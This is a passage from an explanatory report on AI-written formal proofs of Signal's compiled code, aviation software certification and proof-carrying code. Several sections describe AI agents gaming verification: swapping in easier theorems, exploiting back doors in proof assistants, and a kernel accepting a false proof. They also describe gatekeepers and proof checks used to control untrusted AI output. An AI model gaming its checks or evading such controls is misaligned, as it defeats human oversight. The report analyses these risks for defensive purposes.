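The program encrypts the first message with m₁, then keeps c₂ and deletes c₁. Nobody knows a practical way to run F backwards, so a thief who steals c₅ can't work out m₁ to m₄. The thief can still compute m₅, m₆ and so on. To stop this, the two sides regularly exchange fresh keys and mix the result into the chain. The thief can't compute that result just by listening, but can by substituting their own keys, so post-compromise security holds only if the thief doesn't tamper with the exchange.

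### From forward secrecy to a single instruction

Forward secrecy also depends on the handshake, where a single machine instruction can determine whether it holds. Suppose Alice wants to write to Bob while his phone is off. Signal's server gives her Bob's long-term public identity key and a short-term public key that he replaces now and then. Alice uses both to compute the key for her message. (The real handshake uses more keys, including a quantum-resistant one.) If a thief gets Bob's identity key next year, the short-term key still protects the message.

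However, an attacker who controls the server could give Alice their own short-term key in place of Bob's. They would then need only the private half of Bob's identity key to read her message, and could store the message until that key leaked. To prevent this, Bob signs each short-term key with his identity key, and Alice's program checks the signature before continuing.

Symbolic Software (2026) disabled this check in a model of X3DH, Signal's older handshake, by having Alice's program run the check but ignore the result. The bug is realistic because the code still calls the right function with the right arguments. Verifpal, a tool for analysing protocol designs, took 0.28 seconds to find that a message was no longer confidential once the identity keys had leaked.

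On a 64-bit ARM processor, a working check might look roughly like this:

```
bl   verify_signature
cbz  w0, stop
```

The first instruction calls the function that checks the signature. The function puts 1 in the register `w0` if the signature is valid and 0 if it isn't. The second instruction jumps to `stop` if `w0` is 0. In the buggy version, the second instruction is missing.

A proof of forward secrecy for the compiled program must connect these instructions to the goal. The processor model defines what `cbz` does, so if the program continues past it, `w0` was not 0. This means the signature was valid, according to the specification of the signature function. Under a cryptographic assumption, only someone with Bob's identity key could have made that signature. The thief didn't have that key yet, so the short-term key is Bob's. The thief lacks its private half, so stealing the identity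 key later won't reveal the message. Without the second instruction, the first step of this argument fails, even though the design on paper hasn't changed.

The agents also had to connect the rest of the compiled code to the goals. Antipov (2026), in *Шифрование Signal прошло математическую проверку Google. Но вопросы к безопасности остались*, gives the code's size as 560 KB. ARM instructions take four bytes each, so the code has at most about 140,000 instructions, or 46 lines of proof per instruction. OpenNET's example of Claude's RISC-V proofs had 33.

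### The agents and the gatekeeper

AlphaProof Code divides the work so that the agents writing proofs can't change what they have to prove. Researchers guide one agent as it turns Signal's goals into specifications in Lean, and human experts review every specification. A formal model of AArch64, the 64-bit ARM architecture, defines what each machine instruction does. A team of other agents then writes every line of proof on its own. A gatekeeper accepts a proof only if Lean's kernel confirms that it proves the approved specification.

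The gatekeeper is there because agents under pressure to finish a proof look for easier things to prove, such as the correctness of a database that never carries out a write. In *Why Lean?* (de Moura, 2026), the mathematician Terence Tao warns that reinforcement learning is very good at finding such back doors in proof assistants. *The Prover Is the Judge* (2026) applies the same principle in another language, SPARK, and treats the coding agent as an unreliable producer whose work other tools must check.

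A gatekeeper can't check whether the approved specification is a good one. An AI agent drafted the specifications here, so human approval matters a great deal. An auditor would want to know which experts approved which statements, and whether those experts included Signal's own developers.

The agents also audited the finished proof and flagged parts for people to look at. According to DeepMind's announcement, quoted in Schneier's *Formal Verification of the Signal Protocol Using AI* (2026), these parts make up 1% of the codebase. One per cent of the proof would be about 65,000 lines, more than the 26,000 that the paper counts as trusted. The flagged parts may therefore include intermediate definitions, which the kernel already checks but which can help a person understand the argument.

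### Perfect cryptography or merely strong cryptography

The theorems come in two kinds, which make different assumptions about the cryptography.

The symbolic proofs treat an encrypted message as a box that opens only with the right key. As positive-intentions' *ProVerif Verification* explains for a similar tool, the attacker can intercept, modify and send messages but can't break the cryptography. This approach is well suited to finding logical mistakes, such as the ignored signature check. But because symbolic proofs assume perfect encryption, they can't show how well the actual bytes hide a message.

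The computational proofs treat messages as strings of bits and the attacker as a program with limited computing time. They give the attacker some chance of success and show that it is small if the underlying cryptography is strong. In outline, such a theorem usually has this form:

chance of breaking the protocol ≤ chance of breaking the key exchange + chance of breaking the encryption + chance of forging a signature

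Real theorems have more terms and multiply some of them by the number of conversations. The inequality holds because anyone who could break the protocol could use the same method to break one of its ingredients. The terms on the right are assumed to be small. If somebody found a fast way to break the key exchange, the theorem would still be true, but it would no longer guarantee much security.

According to EconoTimes' *Google DeepMind Uses AlphaProof Code to Verify a Compiled Signal Harness* (2026), the computational proofs cover the confidentiality and authenticity of messages, forward secrecy and post-compromise security, but only against attackers with conventional computers. A symbolic proof covers the secrecy of the handshake against an attacker with a future quantum computer. A symbolic model can represent such a computer by letting the attacker break the conventional cryptography.

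No theorem yet combines the realism of the computational model with a quantum attacker. This matters most for SPQR, the part that turned Signal's earlier Double Ratchet into the Triple Ratchet. Signal added it so that conversations could recover from a theft of keys even if the attacker had a quantum computer. As anoni.net points out, the proof shows only that the Triple Ratchet is no weaker than the Double Ratchet. So an auditor can conclude that SPQR doesn't weaken the older protections, but the theorems don't establish that it provides the recovery Signal added it for.

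### Five people and four weeks

The proofs run to about 6.5 million lines of Lean and establish ten theorems. The web summary in *Formal Verification of Signal's Protocol with Gemini* (Kohli and Chaudhuri, 2026) says "over three million", but the 6.5 million figure comes from the paper. Five people completed the proof work in four weeks, or at most 20 person-weeks.

Verifying the seL4 kernel took people about 20 person-years and produced about 200,000 lines of proof, according to *Machine-Generated Code Deserves Machine-Checked Proofs* (2026). Signal's proofs are more than 30 times as long and took roughly a fiftieth of the labour. The comparison is rough, because the projects proved different things about different software and the four weeks presumably don't include developing AlphaProof Code. Still, differences in accounting alone are unlikely to explain a gap this large.

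Google told WIRED that the approach is computationally demanding, and Chaudhuri said there was "a long distance to go" before it could work for all software, according to VPNLab. Without a price for the computing, a company that wants similar proofs can't tell whether the approach would save money or only people's time.

### Putting two old bugs back

Expert review doesn't reliably catch weak specifications. Experts had reviewed the specifications in VeriContest, for example, and 60 postconditions still turned out to be incomplete. The Signal researchers therefore tested their specifications on code they knew to be faulty. They reintroduced two real vulnerabilities that Signal had fixed long ago into an isolated copy of the code. For each faulty version, AlphaProof Code produced a machine-checked proof that the program violates one of the symbolic security theorems.

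To prove a violation in the old versions, the agents had to show that an attack exists that meets all the theorem's conditions and breaks its conclusion. This is a stronger result than a failed proof attempt, although WIRED reported that the old versions "could not be formally verified".

This also shows that the specification rules out some programs. If every program satisfied it, nobody could prove that the old versions violated it. Nor could anyone prove that a program violates a theorem whose conditions are impossible to meet, such as the one about SP1's SLTI instruction, which required a number to be both 0 and 1. Had Succinct and Nethermind tried to prove that a deliberately broken SLTI violated that theorem, they would have failed and might have noticed the mistake.

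Two bugs are a small sample, though. The researchers may have had these two in mind when they approved the specifications, in which case other bugs would be a harder test. Both bugs also violated symbolic theorems, so they provide no direct evidence about the computational theorems.

An auditor could extend the test by removing each security check from the code in turn, perhaps starting with the branch after the signature check, and asking the agents to prove that some theorem now fails. If they can't, the check may be redundant, or it may protect something the specification leaves out. This is mutation testing applied to a specification, and it would have taken far too much work when people wrote the proofs.

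The agents found no new vulnerabilities in the parts of libsignal they verified, which isn't surprising because experts have studied the code for years. Claude found hundreds of bugs when it tried to prove that less carefully studied libraries don't crash.

### Reading 26,000 lines

In a comment on Schneier's post, Clive Robinson asked who would read six million lines of proof, when a 350-page paperback has about 10,000 lines. Nobody has to read the proofs, because the kernel has checked them, but someone has to read the roughly 26,000 lines of specifications and processor model they rest on. That is more than two and a half of Robinson's paperbacks, and much harder to read. At an illustrative 100 lines an hour, one person would need six and a half working weeks, about a third of the labour that went into the proofs.

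About 8,000 of those lines describe how machine code behaves. They are probably easier to trust than the rest, because engineers can test them against a physical processor. *LNSym*, another Lean model of ARM machine code, includes such tests, which run only on a computer with an ARM processor. The effort of reviewing a processor model is also easier to justify, since other projects can use the same model.

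The other 18,000 lines are specifications and definitions, which have no physical counterpart to test against. A reader needs to know both Lean and cryptography, and has to check details that a property's name leaves out. For example, in Symbolic Software's (2026) model of Signal's older handshake, five of six security queries passed. The sixth failed because Bob can't fully authenticate Alice's first message until the two have exchanged a reply. Signal documents this as a tradeoff for letting people write to someone who is offline. So a reader who sees a theorem called "authentication" has to find out which messages it covers, and from what point in the conversation.

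Dividing the reading among specialists would help. A cryptographer could read the final theorems and the definition of the attacker, and an ARM engineer could read the processor model. Someone would still need to check that the parts fit together, because a mistake in an intermediate definition can change the meaning of every theorem that uses it.

### What the theorems leave to others

The proofs cover a harness, a small command-line program linked to libsignal version 0.105.4 that sets up one-to-one conversations and exchanges messages. They don't cover group chats, the feature that hides who sent a message, or the phone apps. The researchers expect their results to carry over to the apps if the apps run the protocol code unchanged. As with the RISC-V proofs, that expectation is reasonable for mistakes in the source code but not for compiler errors. Each new version of libsignal needs new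 proofs, or at least a check that the old ones still apply.

The proofs leave out some code that every conversation depends on. The researchers did not verify the code that generates keys. If it produced the same key on every phone, anyone could read everyone's messages, yet the theorems would still be true because they assume properly generated keys. The researchers also assume that the basic cryptographic functions meet their specifications. Microsoft's *Verifying Rust cryptography in SymCrypt, from standards to code* explains that a single arithmetic error can undermine such a function, and describes machine-checked proofs to prevent such errors. Those proofs cover Microsoft's library, so they don't show that the functions Signal uses are correct.

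The most important assumption may be that both people have each other's identity keys from the start. In practice, a phone normally gets a stranger's identity key from Signal's server, which the theorems otherwise assume is hostile. A hostile server could supply its own key and pose as the stranger. Users can detect this by comparing a code in Signal, but a proof can't ensure that they do.

The proofs also exclude side channels, such as timing or power use that leaks secrets, so engineers have to look for these in other ways. *The Prover Is the Judge* describes a project that ran two timing tests, TIMECOP and dudect, alongside its proofs. The theorems don't cover other secrets left in memory or accounts used on several devices either.

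Symbolic Software (2026) reported two severe vulnerabilities in hpke-rs, a library that one of Signal's components uses. One of them broke forward secrecy. The library implements an encryption standard that the theorems do not cover, so a valid proof about PQXDH would not have revealed either vulnerability.

Encryption protects messages only between the phones. Someone who can see the screen, or who has installed spyware, can read them without breaking the encryption. Encryption still stops anyone who can only watch the network, so another commenter on Schneier's blog seems too harsh in calling a system without secure endpoints "worse than nothing". The theorems also don't cover what Signal's servers record about users. In October 2026, a US grand jury subpoenaed Signal for information about four phone numbers. Only one had an account, and Signal supplied its creation time and last connection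 date. Signal could supply so little because its policy is to collect little.

### Outside judgements

Few independent assessments exist so far. The cryptographer Bruce Schneier wrote that the work "seems like a good thing" but gave no technical verdict. Signal's chief technology officer, Ehren Kret, who is not an independent assessor, said it increased his confidence in the code. The specifications and proofs are public, but as of November 14, four days after the announcement, anoni.net had found no reproduction by other researchers.

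The cryptographer Nadim Kobeissi had earlier proposed a useful standard for such announcements. According to Red Sky Alliance's *When Computer-Proven Security Leaves Room for Doubt*, he uses the term "verification theatre" for projects that prove selected components but use language that implies broader coverage, without disclosing the difference. The paper by Chaudhuri and colleagues does well by this standard because it lists its exclusions in detail. Some press coverage does worse, including a headline that said the analysis proves both Signal's and WhatsApp's encryption secure, although the researchers never examined WhatsApp's software.

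A second project, Signal Shot, may provide a more thorough check. Signal, the Beneficial AI Foundation and Lean's developers are working together to verify the protocol and its Rust code, according to Lean FRO (2026). Bhargavan (2026) reports in *Software Verification in Lean* that the project was presented to other researchers in Paris in April as a challenge to the whole community. The team plans to translate the Rust source code into Lean with a tool called Aeneas and prove that the translation meets the specification. That approach isn't tied to ARM processors, but anyone relying on it has to trust the translator and the Rust compiler.

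Two of the AlphaProof Code researchers sit with de Moura on the steering committee of CSLib, a Lean library that Signal Shot uses, so the two projects are not fully independent. But if Signal Shot's team writes its own specifications, someone could try to prove that they agree with DeepMind's. Any disagreement would point to a mistake, or to a difference in what the teams think Signal guarantees, that neither the kernel nor the two old bugs could reveal.

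## Aircraft software: what certifiers accept as tests and proofs

Signal's developers could release their code without approval, but an aircraft maker has to convince a regulator that its software is safe before an airliner can carry passengers. The aviation industry has therefore had decades to work out what evidence an outsider should accept. Most of that evidence is reviews and tests. Since 2011, the industry's main standard has also allowed proofs to replace some tests.

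The standard for aircraft software is DO-178C, called ED-12C in Europe. In its guidance document *AMC 20-115D* (2017), the European Union Aviation Safety Agency (EASA) accepts it as one way, but not the only way, to show that software meets the regulations. The American regulator, the FAA, has closely matching guidance. In 2019 the two agencies set up a joint task force to develop a way of judging other standards that a manufacturer might use instead.

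### From a requirement to a line of code

DO-178C has five levels, and a program's level depends on the worst effect its failure could have. Higher levels require more evidence, including tests that exercise the code more thoroughly.

| Level | Worst effect of a failure | What the tests must exercise |
|---|---|---|
| A | Catastrophic, such as loss of the aircraft | Every condition within every decision (MC/DC) |
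| B | Hazardous | Every decision, with both outcomes |
| C | Major | Every statement |
| D | Minor | No rule about code coverage |
| E | None | Nothing |

Suppose an aircraft has thrust reversers, which redirect the engines' thrust forwards to slow the plane after landing. They must not open in flight. Engineers use this requirement for the whole aircraft to write a high-level requirement for the software: allow reverse thrust only if the pilot has selected it and the aircraft is on the ground. A low-level requirement, detailed enough to code from, defines "on the ground" as a signal from the left or right main wheels. The engineers keep records that link each requirement to the one it came from, to the code that implements it and to the tests that check it.

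Developers also have to trace the code back to the requirements. Code that doesn't trace to any requirement counts as "extraneous", and DO-178C requires developers to show that there is none. This rule is useful for AI-written code because an agent can add features that nobody asked for.

Engineers write the tests from the requirements, not from the code. Souyris, Wiels and colleagues explain in *Formal Verification of Avionics Software Products* that the tests must include abnormal inputs as well as normal ones. The engineers measure coverage only after writing these tests. If the tests never run a line of code, a test may be missing, a requirement may be missing, or the line may have no purpose. An AI agent that had to reach 100% coverage could read the code and write tests that record what the code does, which would meet the target but hide all three problems.

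At levels A and B, someone other than the author must do much of the checking. V-Model Extension's *DO-178C*, a page about a tool for AI-assisted development, argues that the tool's scripts provide this independence because the AI model that wrote the software doesn't produce the coverage reports. This argument is reasonable for counting links and tests. But scripts that match patterns in text can't determine whether a requirement makes sense or an expected result is right, so a level A program would still need an independent reader.

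### Four tests for one condition

MC/DC, the coverage rule for level A, stands for modified condition/decision coverage. The tests must show that each condition can change the outcome by itself while the others stay the same. In the example, the software allows reverse thrust if

A and (B or C)

where A means that the pilot has selected it, B that the left wheels are on the ground, and C that the right wheels are. Four tests are enough:

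| Test | A | B | C | Reverse thrust allowed? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Yes | Yes | No | Yes |
| 2 | No | Yes | No | No |
| 3 | Yes | No | No | No |
| 4 | Yes | No | Yes | Yes |

Tests 1 and 2 differ only in A, and their outcomes differ, so A affects the outcome by itself. Tests 1 and 3 show the same for B, and tests 3 and 4 for C. A decision with n separate conditions needs at least n + 1 tests, whereas trying every combination takes 2^n. With 20 conditions, that is at least 21 tests, compared with more than a million.

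The rule for level B requires only one test with each outcome, so tests 1 and 2 would be enough. But if the programmer reads the right-hand sensor backwards and writes "A and (B or not C)", both tests still pass. Test 3 fails, because the faulty code allows reverse thrust with all the wheels in the air.

MC/DC can miss mistakes too. If the programmer puts the brackets in the wrong place and writes "(A and B) or C", all four tests pass, and they also satisfy MC/DC for the faulty code. Yet this version would let the reversers open in flight, without any command from the pilot, if the right-hand sensor wrongly signalled contact with the ground. A proof that the code meets the low-level requirement would fail, because it has to cover all eight combinations. (For three conditions, so would eight tests.)

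Tests and proofs check code against its requirements, but neither can show whether the requirements are right, including whether an "or" should have been an "and". In September 1993, an Airbus A320 landed in Warsaw on its right wheels, about nine seconds before the left ones touched down. The aircraft's logic allowed reverse thrust only with weight on both sides, so the reversers stayed shut until then. The plane overran the runway, and two people died. Investigators mainly blamed the crew's decisions, but also cited design features that limited the use of the brakes. Code for that logic could have passed every test and proof based on its requirements.

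This fits the industry's general experience. Moy and Ledinot (2013), in *Testing or Formal Verification*, write that since the previous version of the standard appeared in 1992, nobody had attributed a death to software that failed to implement its requirements. Errors found in service tend to be in the requirements themselves. To achieve this record, some projects spend up to seven times as much on verification as on the rest of development.

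### One failure in a billion hours

For catastrophic failures, aviation authorities want a rate of around one in a billion flight hours. In 1993, NASA researchers Butler and Finelli argued in *The Infeasibility of Quantifying the Reliability of Life-Critical Real-Time Software* that no practical amount of testing could show that software fails this rarely.

If a program fails at a constant rate of λ per hour, the chance that it runs for T hours without failing is

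e^(−λT)

With λ = 10^(−9), this falls to 5% when T is about 3 billion hours, so the program must run that long without a failure to support the required rate with 95% confidence. (This is the 3/n bound again, with hours instead of test runs.) The test would take about 342,000 years on one computer, 3,400 years on a hundred, and 34 years on 10,000. Butler and Finelli note that the cost of such systems rarely allowed tests on more than ten copies. If the program fails once and somebody repairs it, the count of failure-free hours restarts from zero.

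Predicting reliability from how it improves as engineers fix bugs can still require impractically long testing. Butler and Finelli tried this with data from an earlier experiment. In one program, the chance of failure per input fell from 98% to under 0.1% as the programmers removed the first six bugs. If the trend continued, the program would reach a failure rate of one in a billion ten-hour flights after they had removed 23 bugs, and finding the last of those would take about 340,000 years.

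Another idea is to run three separately written versions of the software and take a majority vote. If each version fails once in 100,000 hours and the failures are independent, two will fail together only about three times in 10 billion hours. But if a shared mistake makes them fail together once in 10 million hours, the system will fail more than 300 times as often as calculated, and a 100-year test would probably not reveal the mistake. The same problem would affect a vote among AI models, which also share mistakes.

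Cheap computing has weakened part of the argument. A million simulated copies could accumulate 3 billion hours in about four months. At an illustrative two cents per copy per hour, this would cost $60 million, which is affordable for a new airliner project. But the simulation would have to include rare situations as often as they occur in real flight. If it left out one that arises every 100 million hours and always makes the software fail, the true failure rate would be at least ten times the target, and the test would not reveal it. Testers would also need a reliable way to judge all the outputs.

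The conclusion also depends on the type of system. Butler and Finelli calculate that if a program receives one input a day and each test takes a tenth of a second, the necessary testing takes just over a year. Flight controls are a much harder case because they receive ten or more inputs per second. Ashmore (2014), in *The Utility and Practicality of Quantifying Software Reliability*, argues that reliability can be measured in at least one meaningful case, and that developers who only follow a standard may miss chances to reduce risk.

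Certifiers therefore rely heavily on how people developed the software. Souyris and colleagues explain that the standard emphasises the quality of the development process because traditional methods can't prove the absence of errors. This makes AI-written code awkward to certify, since it's unclear what a sound process means for a language model. A proof avoids this difficulty because it is about the program itself.

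### How Airbus replaced unit tests with proofs

DO-333, a supplement to the standard, explains how to use proofs for certification. A proof doesn't run the program, so it makes no sense to measure which lines ran. Engineers have to do four things instead. They show that every requirement has a proof, and justify each assumption the proofs make. They show that the requirements specify an output for every input. They check that data flows only where the design intended. They look for extraneous code by review or some other method that isn't formal.

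Checking the requirements for completeness is a good defence against vacuous proofs. Suppose a specification states only that the software must allow reverse thrust when A and (B or C) is true. Code that always allowed it, even in flight, would meet that specification. A completeness check would expose this because the specification gives no output for the remaining cases. It would also have caught most of the verified Dafny programs that Vempaty and colleagues examined, since those had no postcondition. But as Moy and Ledinot acknowledge, formal methods can't find every forgotten requirement.

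Airbus began using proofs before DO-333 existed, with permission from the certification authorities. Since 2002, its engineers have replaced some unit tests with "unit proofs" for parts of the critical software on the A380, the A350 and the A400M military transport. They write each low-level requirement as preconditions and postconditions, and list the data each function may use. A programmer then writes the function in C. A tool called Caveat identifies the data the code actually uses, so that an engineer can compare it with the design. Caveat also tries to prove that the postconditions hold whenever the preconditions do, and the engineer deals with whatever it can't prove automatically.

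The new method changed only the detailed design and unit verification stages, according to Duprat, Favre-Felix and Souyris, in *Formal Verification Workbench for Airbus Avionics Software*. Much of the testing remained, for several reasons:

- Caveat proves each function separately, with stand-ins for the functions it calls. It can't detect that a programmer has misunderstood what another function does, so the engineers test the parts together.
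- The high-level requirements are in ordinary language, which a prover can't use.
- Tests on the aircraft's own computers check timing and the connection between software and hardware. They also find faults in the hardware, which is often new as well.

The engineers also have to show that the compiler preserves what they proved about the source code. Military Embedded Systems describes a related check for SPARK programs, in which developers run the integration tests with the contracts switched on as run-time checks, run them again with the contracts off, and compare the outputs.

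Dassault Aviation, which makes business jets, used proofs to check how its flight-control software handles abnormal inputs. Its engineers had previously argued by hand that a few hundred conditions, mostly limits on the size of numbers, would always hold. Automatic analysis proved about 85% of them, and a more laborious kind of proof dealt with the rest. The set-up took about a person-month, roughly as long as the manual analysis it replaced. The company therefore saved no time on the first release, but about a person-month on each later one.

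Moy, Ledinot and their co-authors say that unit proof takes less effort overall than unit testing, mainly because it makes maintenance easier. They were not neutral, since Ledinot worked for Dassault and another co-author, Hervé Delseny, worked for Airbus. Delseny also helped write DO-178C and, with Brown and other colleagues, described the proposed rules on formal methods before they were published.

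*Formalise to automate*, a later Airbus paper by Brahmi, Delmas and colleagues (2018), is less enthusiastic. It reports that proof had so far had a limited effect on efficiency, partly because preparing the inputs for the proof tools took so much work. Airbus was therefore introducing a process in which an engineer writes each low-level requirement once, in a formal language, and a compiler turns it into either a contract for a prover or an oracle for tests. Every function must have either a proof or enough tests to meet the coverage rule for its level. Tests remain necessary for assembly code and C code that doesn't suit the prover.

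The process also makes some assumptions easier to trust. For example, the prover assumes calculations never overflow, and a separate tool, Astrée, checks this for the whole program. Airbus was also moving to the verified compiler CompCert for its most critical software. The company's target was to cut the cost of design and unit verification by 75%.

Brahmi and colleagues put verification at about 70% of Airbus's development costs for this kind of software. If AI made everything except verification free, the total would fall by only about 30%. Any larger savings would have to come from cheaper tests and proofs, where careless use of AI could also do the most damage.

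### AI tools under aviation rules

Another document, DO-330, covers the software tools engineers use. If a tool replaces a required activity and nobody checks its output, it needs "qualification", meaning evidence that it works properly for its purpose. There are five levels, and the strictest applies to tools that could put a mistake into the most critical software, such as code generators. A verification tool can only overlook mistakes, so its developers have to provide less evidence. Airbus qualified Caveat as a verification tool. According to Souyris and colleagues, this involves running the tool on representative cases and checking that it gives the expected results.

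Testing a proof checker on representative cases works well when engineers want their proofs to be valid. Such cases would be unlikely to include the strange construction that made Lean's kernel accept a false proof in July 2026. If AI agents write the proofs, the checker's test cases should therefore include known attacks.

Current language models don't fit these rules. *Introduction AI based tooling* (June 2026), from ELISA, a project on using Linux in safety-critical systems, pointed out that a model's results are probabilistic, while qualification depends on predictable behaviour. It concluded that a human must stay in the loop until the standard changes.

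An unpredictable tool may still be acceptable if something else checks its output. In a discussion paper for a conference of aviation authorities in September 2026, EASA (2026) wrote: "Tools whose outputs are fully and independently verified may not require qualification." If people rely on a tool's output without such checks, the tool should be qualified to a level that matches the risk.

Regulators could apply the same principle to AI-written code, though the paper doesn't specifically do so. If an AI model finds a proof and a qualified checker accepts it, nobody should need to qualify the model. AI-written code could go through the same reviews, tests and coverage analysis as code from a human programmer, who doesn't need qualification as a tool either. A person who understands the aircraft would still have to approve the specification.

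That person also needs enough time and knowledge to disagree with the model. EASA similarly writes that simply placing a human "in the loop" isn't enough for AI systems in operation.

Most of the regulators' recent work is about AI on board aircraft or in air traffic control. In November 2025, EASA proposed detailed specifications for trustworthy AI in aviation. In June 2026, it also published a draft of its third concept paper on AI (EASA, 2026), which extends the guidance to systems that may operate with no human present. The FAA's position on AI-written aircraft code is less clear. The FAA's notice *Use of Generative AI Tools and Services* (2025) applied to the agency's own employees and contractors.

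Standards bodies are working on more specific rules. ELISA's *Facilitated feedback and discussion and comparison of markets views* (2026) lists a draft international standard, ISO 22440, with an appendix on qualifying AI tools. It also lists ED-324, an aviation standard due for publication at the end of 2026. ED-324 mainly covers products that contain AI.

Companies aren't waiting for these standards. AdaCore's *AI Code Generation for Safety-Critical Software* advertises a product that combines AI-written code with SPARK proofs and links to the requirements. This follows EASA's principle, but a buyer would still have to ask who approves the specifications.

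### Test records under the Cyber Resilience Act

Most software never goes through anything like aircraft certification. The European Union's Cyber Resilience Act will require some evidence for most commercial products that contain software and can connect to a device or network. Its main obligations apply from December 11, 2027. Manufacturers have had to report actively exploited vulnerabilities and severe security incidents since September 11, 2026.

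The act requires technical documentation for each product. This must include a description of the design, an assessment of the security risks, and reports of the tests the manufacturer ran to check that the product and the manufacturer's process for handling vulnerabilities meet the act's security requirements. The manufacturer must keep the documentation available to the authorities for at least ten years after selling the product, or for the support period if that is longer.

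This requirement is much weaker than those in DO-178C. The act doesn't require proofs, a particular level of code coverage or a test author other than the programmer. For most products, manufacturers can do the assessment themselves. The reports concern security, so they needn't show that the software gives the right answers. Aircraft products with EU aviation certification are exempt because they already have their own rules.

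Still, a manufacturer that sells AI-written software in Europe will have to keep test reports that an official can ask to see. Recording who or what wrote each test would take little extra work.

### An evidence package for AI-written code

The aviation standards already cover most of what a buyer would want with an AI-written component. The table sets out a possible package and marks which parts have a counterpart in DO-178C or its companion documents.

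| Item | What the supplier provides | Counterpart in aviation |
|---|---|---|
| Stated intent | The customer's own description, with approved examples | Yes: system requirements |
| Specification | Precise requirements, their authors, and the person who approved each one | Yes: software requirements and review records |
| Links | A trail from each requirement to its code, tests and theorems, and back | Yes: trace data |
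| Tests | Tests, results and coverage, the person or model that wrote each test, and whether the coding agent could see it | Partly: there are rules on independence, but not for AI authors |
| Proof | Theorem statements, proof files, the list of axioms and the checker's version | Partly: DO-333 accepts proofs but predates AI-written ones |
| Assumptions | Conditions on callers, surroundings, compiler and hardware, with evidence for each | Yes: DO-333 requires justification |
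| Tools | AI models, compilers and checkers, with evidence for any whose output nobody checks | Partly: DO-330 doesn't suit language models |
| Build provenance | A signed record that ties the source code and evidence to the exact program delivered | Partly: an index lists exact versions, but needs no digital signature |
| Rechecking | Files, commands and tool versions for repeating the tests and proofs | Partly: the records exist, but mainly for the regulator |
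| Known gaps | Open bugs, failed tests, and code without tests or proofs | Partly: a final summary lists known problems |

The entry for tests goes further than the aviation rules because code and tests written by the same model in separate sessions are hardly independent. A buyer who knows which model wrote each can at least take this into account.

Build provenance would have helped in two of the earlier cases. Gunton couldn't tell which release of SP1 the proofs described, and someone who copied the examples in lean-zip's documentation would apparently have run the old C code instead of the proved functions.

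The usual way to identify a program is by its cryptographic hash, a short fingerprint calculated from the whole file, so changing any byte changes the hash. A provenance record gives the program's hash, the version of the source code, and the service that built the program. The build service signs the record so that nobody can alter it unnoticed. For the package in the table, a second signed record should list the hashes of the specification, tests and proofs.

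SLSA (Supply-chain Levels for Software Artifacts) is a widely used framework for provenance records. Its first build level requires that a record exist. The second requires a hosted build service to create and sign it. The third also requires the service to isolate builds from one another and prevent them from accessing the signing key. Protecting the key matters if an AI agent writes the build instructions, because an agent that could use the key could sign a false record.

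Provenance shows where a program came from, not whether it is any good. A build service would also sign the key-value store that never saved its data. A record of the build also does not show that the compiler worked correctly, so the best proof to pair with it is one about the machine code, because the theorem can refer to the same bytes whose hash is in the record.

A buyer can begin with the checks that take the least effort. Comparing the hash takes seconds. Rerunning the tests and the proof checker may take hours, but this is mostly computer time. If these checks pass, a person should read the specification and the assumptions. In the reverse-thrust example, the specification is one line, and one of the assumptions is that the wheel sensors work. An engineer who remembered the Warsaw accident would also ask what happens when the plane lands on one side first.

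## Proposals that software should carry proofs of safety

An evidence package is mainly for customers, who want a program to do what they asked for. People who run a stranger's program often just need to know that it won't do any damage. In 1996 George Necula and Peter Lee of Carnegie Mellon University proposed that such programs should come with a proof that they are safe to run. AI researchers have since proposed much the same for AI systems, drones and machines that make DNA.

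### Proof-carrying code

*Safe Kernel Extensions Without Run-Time Checking* (Necula and Lee, 1996) addresses how an operating-system kernel can determine whether code from an untrusted source is safe to accept. An application can run faster if it installs a little code inside the kernel, but a mistake in that code can corrupt the whole computer.

Under the proposal known as proof-carrying code, the kernel's designers publish a safety policy. The sender of a program proves that it obeys the policy and sends the proof with it. The kernel works out from the program's instructions what the proof needs to establish, and checks that it does. The check doesn't depend on who the sender is or what tools they used.

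Tampering achieves little, because the kernel derives the statement to be proved from the code it receives. Altering the program normally changes that statement, so the old proof no longer fits. If somebody alters both the program and the proof, and the proof is still valid, the altered program also obeys the policy.

In one example, the kernel keeps a table in which each entry has a tag and a piece of data. The policy lets a program change the data in its own entry only if the tag isn't zero. The sample program tests the tag and skips the write if the tag is zero. The proof uses this test to show that the policy permits the write whenever the program reaches it. Without the test, the sender would have to prove that the tag is never zero, which doesn't follow from the policy. The program has seven instructions, and checking its proof took 1.4 milliseconds. The checker was about five pages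 of C.

The main experiment used packet filters, small programs that examine each packet of data arriving from a network and decide whether an application wants it. The policy let a filter read the packet and a small scratch area, and write only to the scratch area. It allowed only forward jumps, so every filter had to finish. Necula and Lee wrote four filters by hand in assembly language:

| What the filter accepts | Instructions | Size with proof (bytes) | Time to check the proof (ms) |
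|---|---|---|---|
| All internet (IP) packets | 8 | 385 | 0.78 |
| IP packets from one network | 15 | 516 | 1.07 |
| IP or ARP packets between two networks | 47 | 1,024 | 2.35 |
| TCP packets for one port | 28 | 814 | 1.71 |

The kernel checks each proof only once, whereas the alternatives check the program while it runs. The interpreted filters that were standard at the time were about ten times slower than the filters with proofs. The filters with proofs also ran about 25% faster than those using software fault isolation, which adds a check to each memory access. The last filter in the table had to process 28,000 packets, or about 28 seconds of traffic on the university's network, before its speed made up for the time spent checking its proof.

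The policy doesn't specify which packets a filter should accept. Its postcondition is "true", so a filter that rejected every packet would pass. This omission is deliberate, though it would be a serious fault in a customer's specification. The policy protects the kernel whatever the sender intended, and a useless filter harms only the application that installed it. One policy also covers every filter, so its designers can justify reviewing it very carefully.

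These programs were easy to verify because none had a loop. Necula and Lee called their own theorem prover a toy and described automatic proof generation as one of the most serious obstacles to practical use. AI has since removed much of that obstacle, as Claude's proofs for 123 libraries show.

### From packet filters to powerful AI

In *Provably safe systems*, Tegmark and Omohundro (2023) propose making proof-carrying code a condition of running powerful AI. They argue that no system, however intelligent, can prove a false statement or do something provably impossible. People could therefore use an AI system they didn't trust if a simple checker approved a proof of safety before each risky action.

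In their plan, AI would discover useful algorithms and rewrite them as proof-carrying code, and an industry standard would require powerful hardware to run only code of this kind. Secure chips would enforce similar rules on physical devices. If terrorists wanted to use AI to design a virus, order its DNA and spread it with drones, the design software would produce only what it could prove safe for humans. The DNA synthesiser and the drones would each need a proof before they operated.

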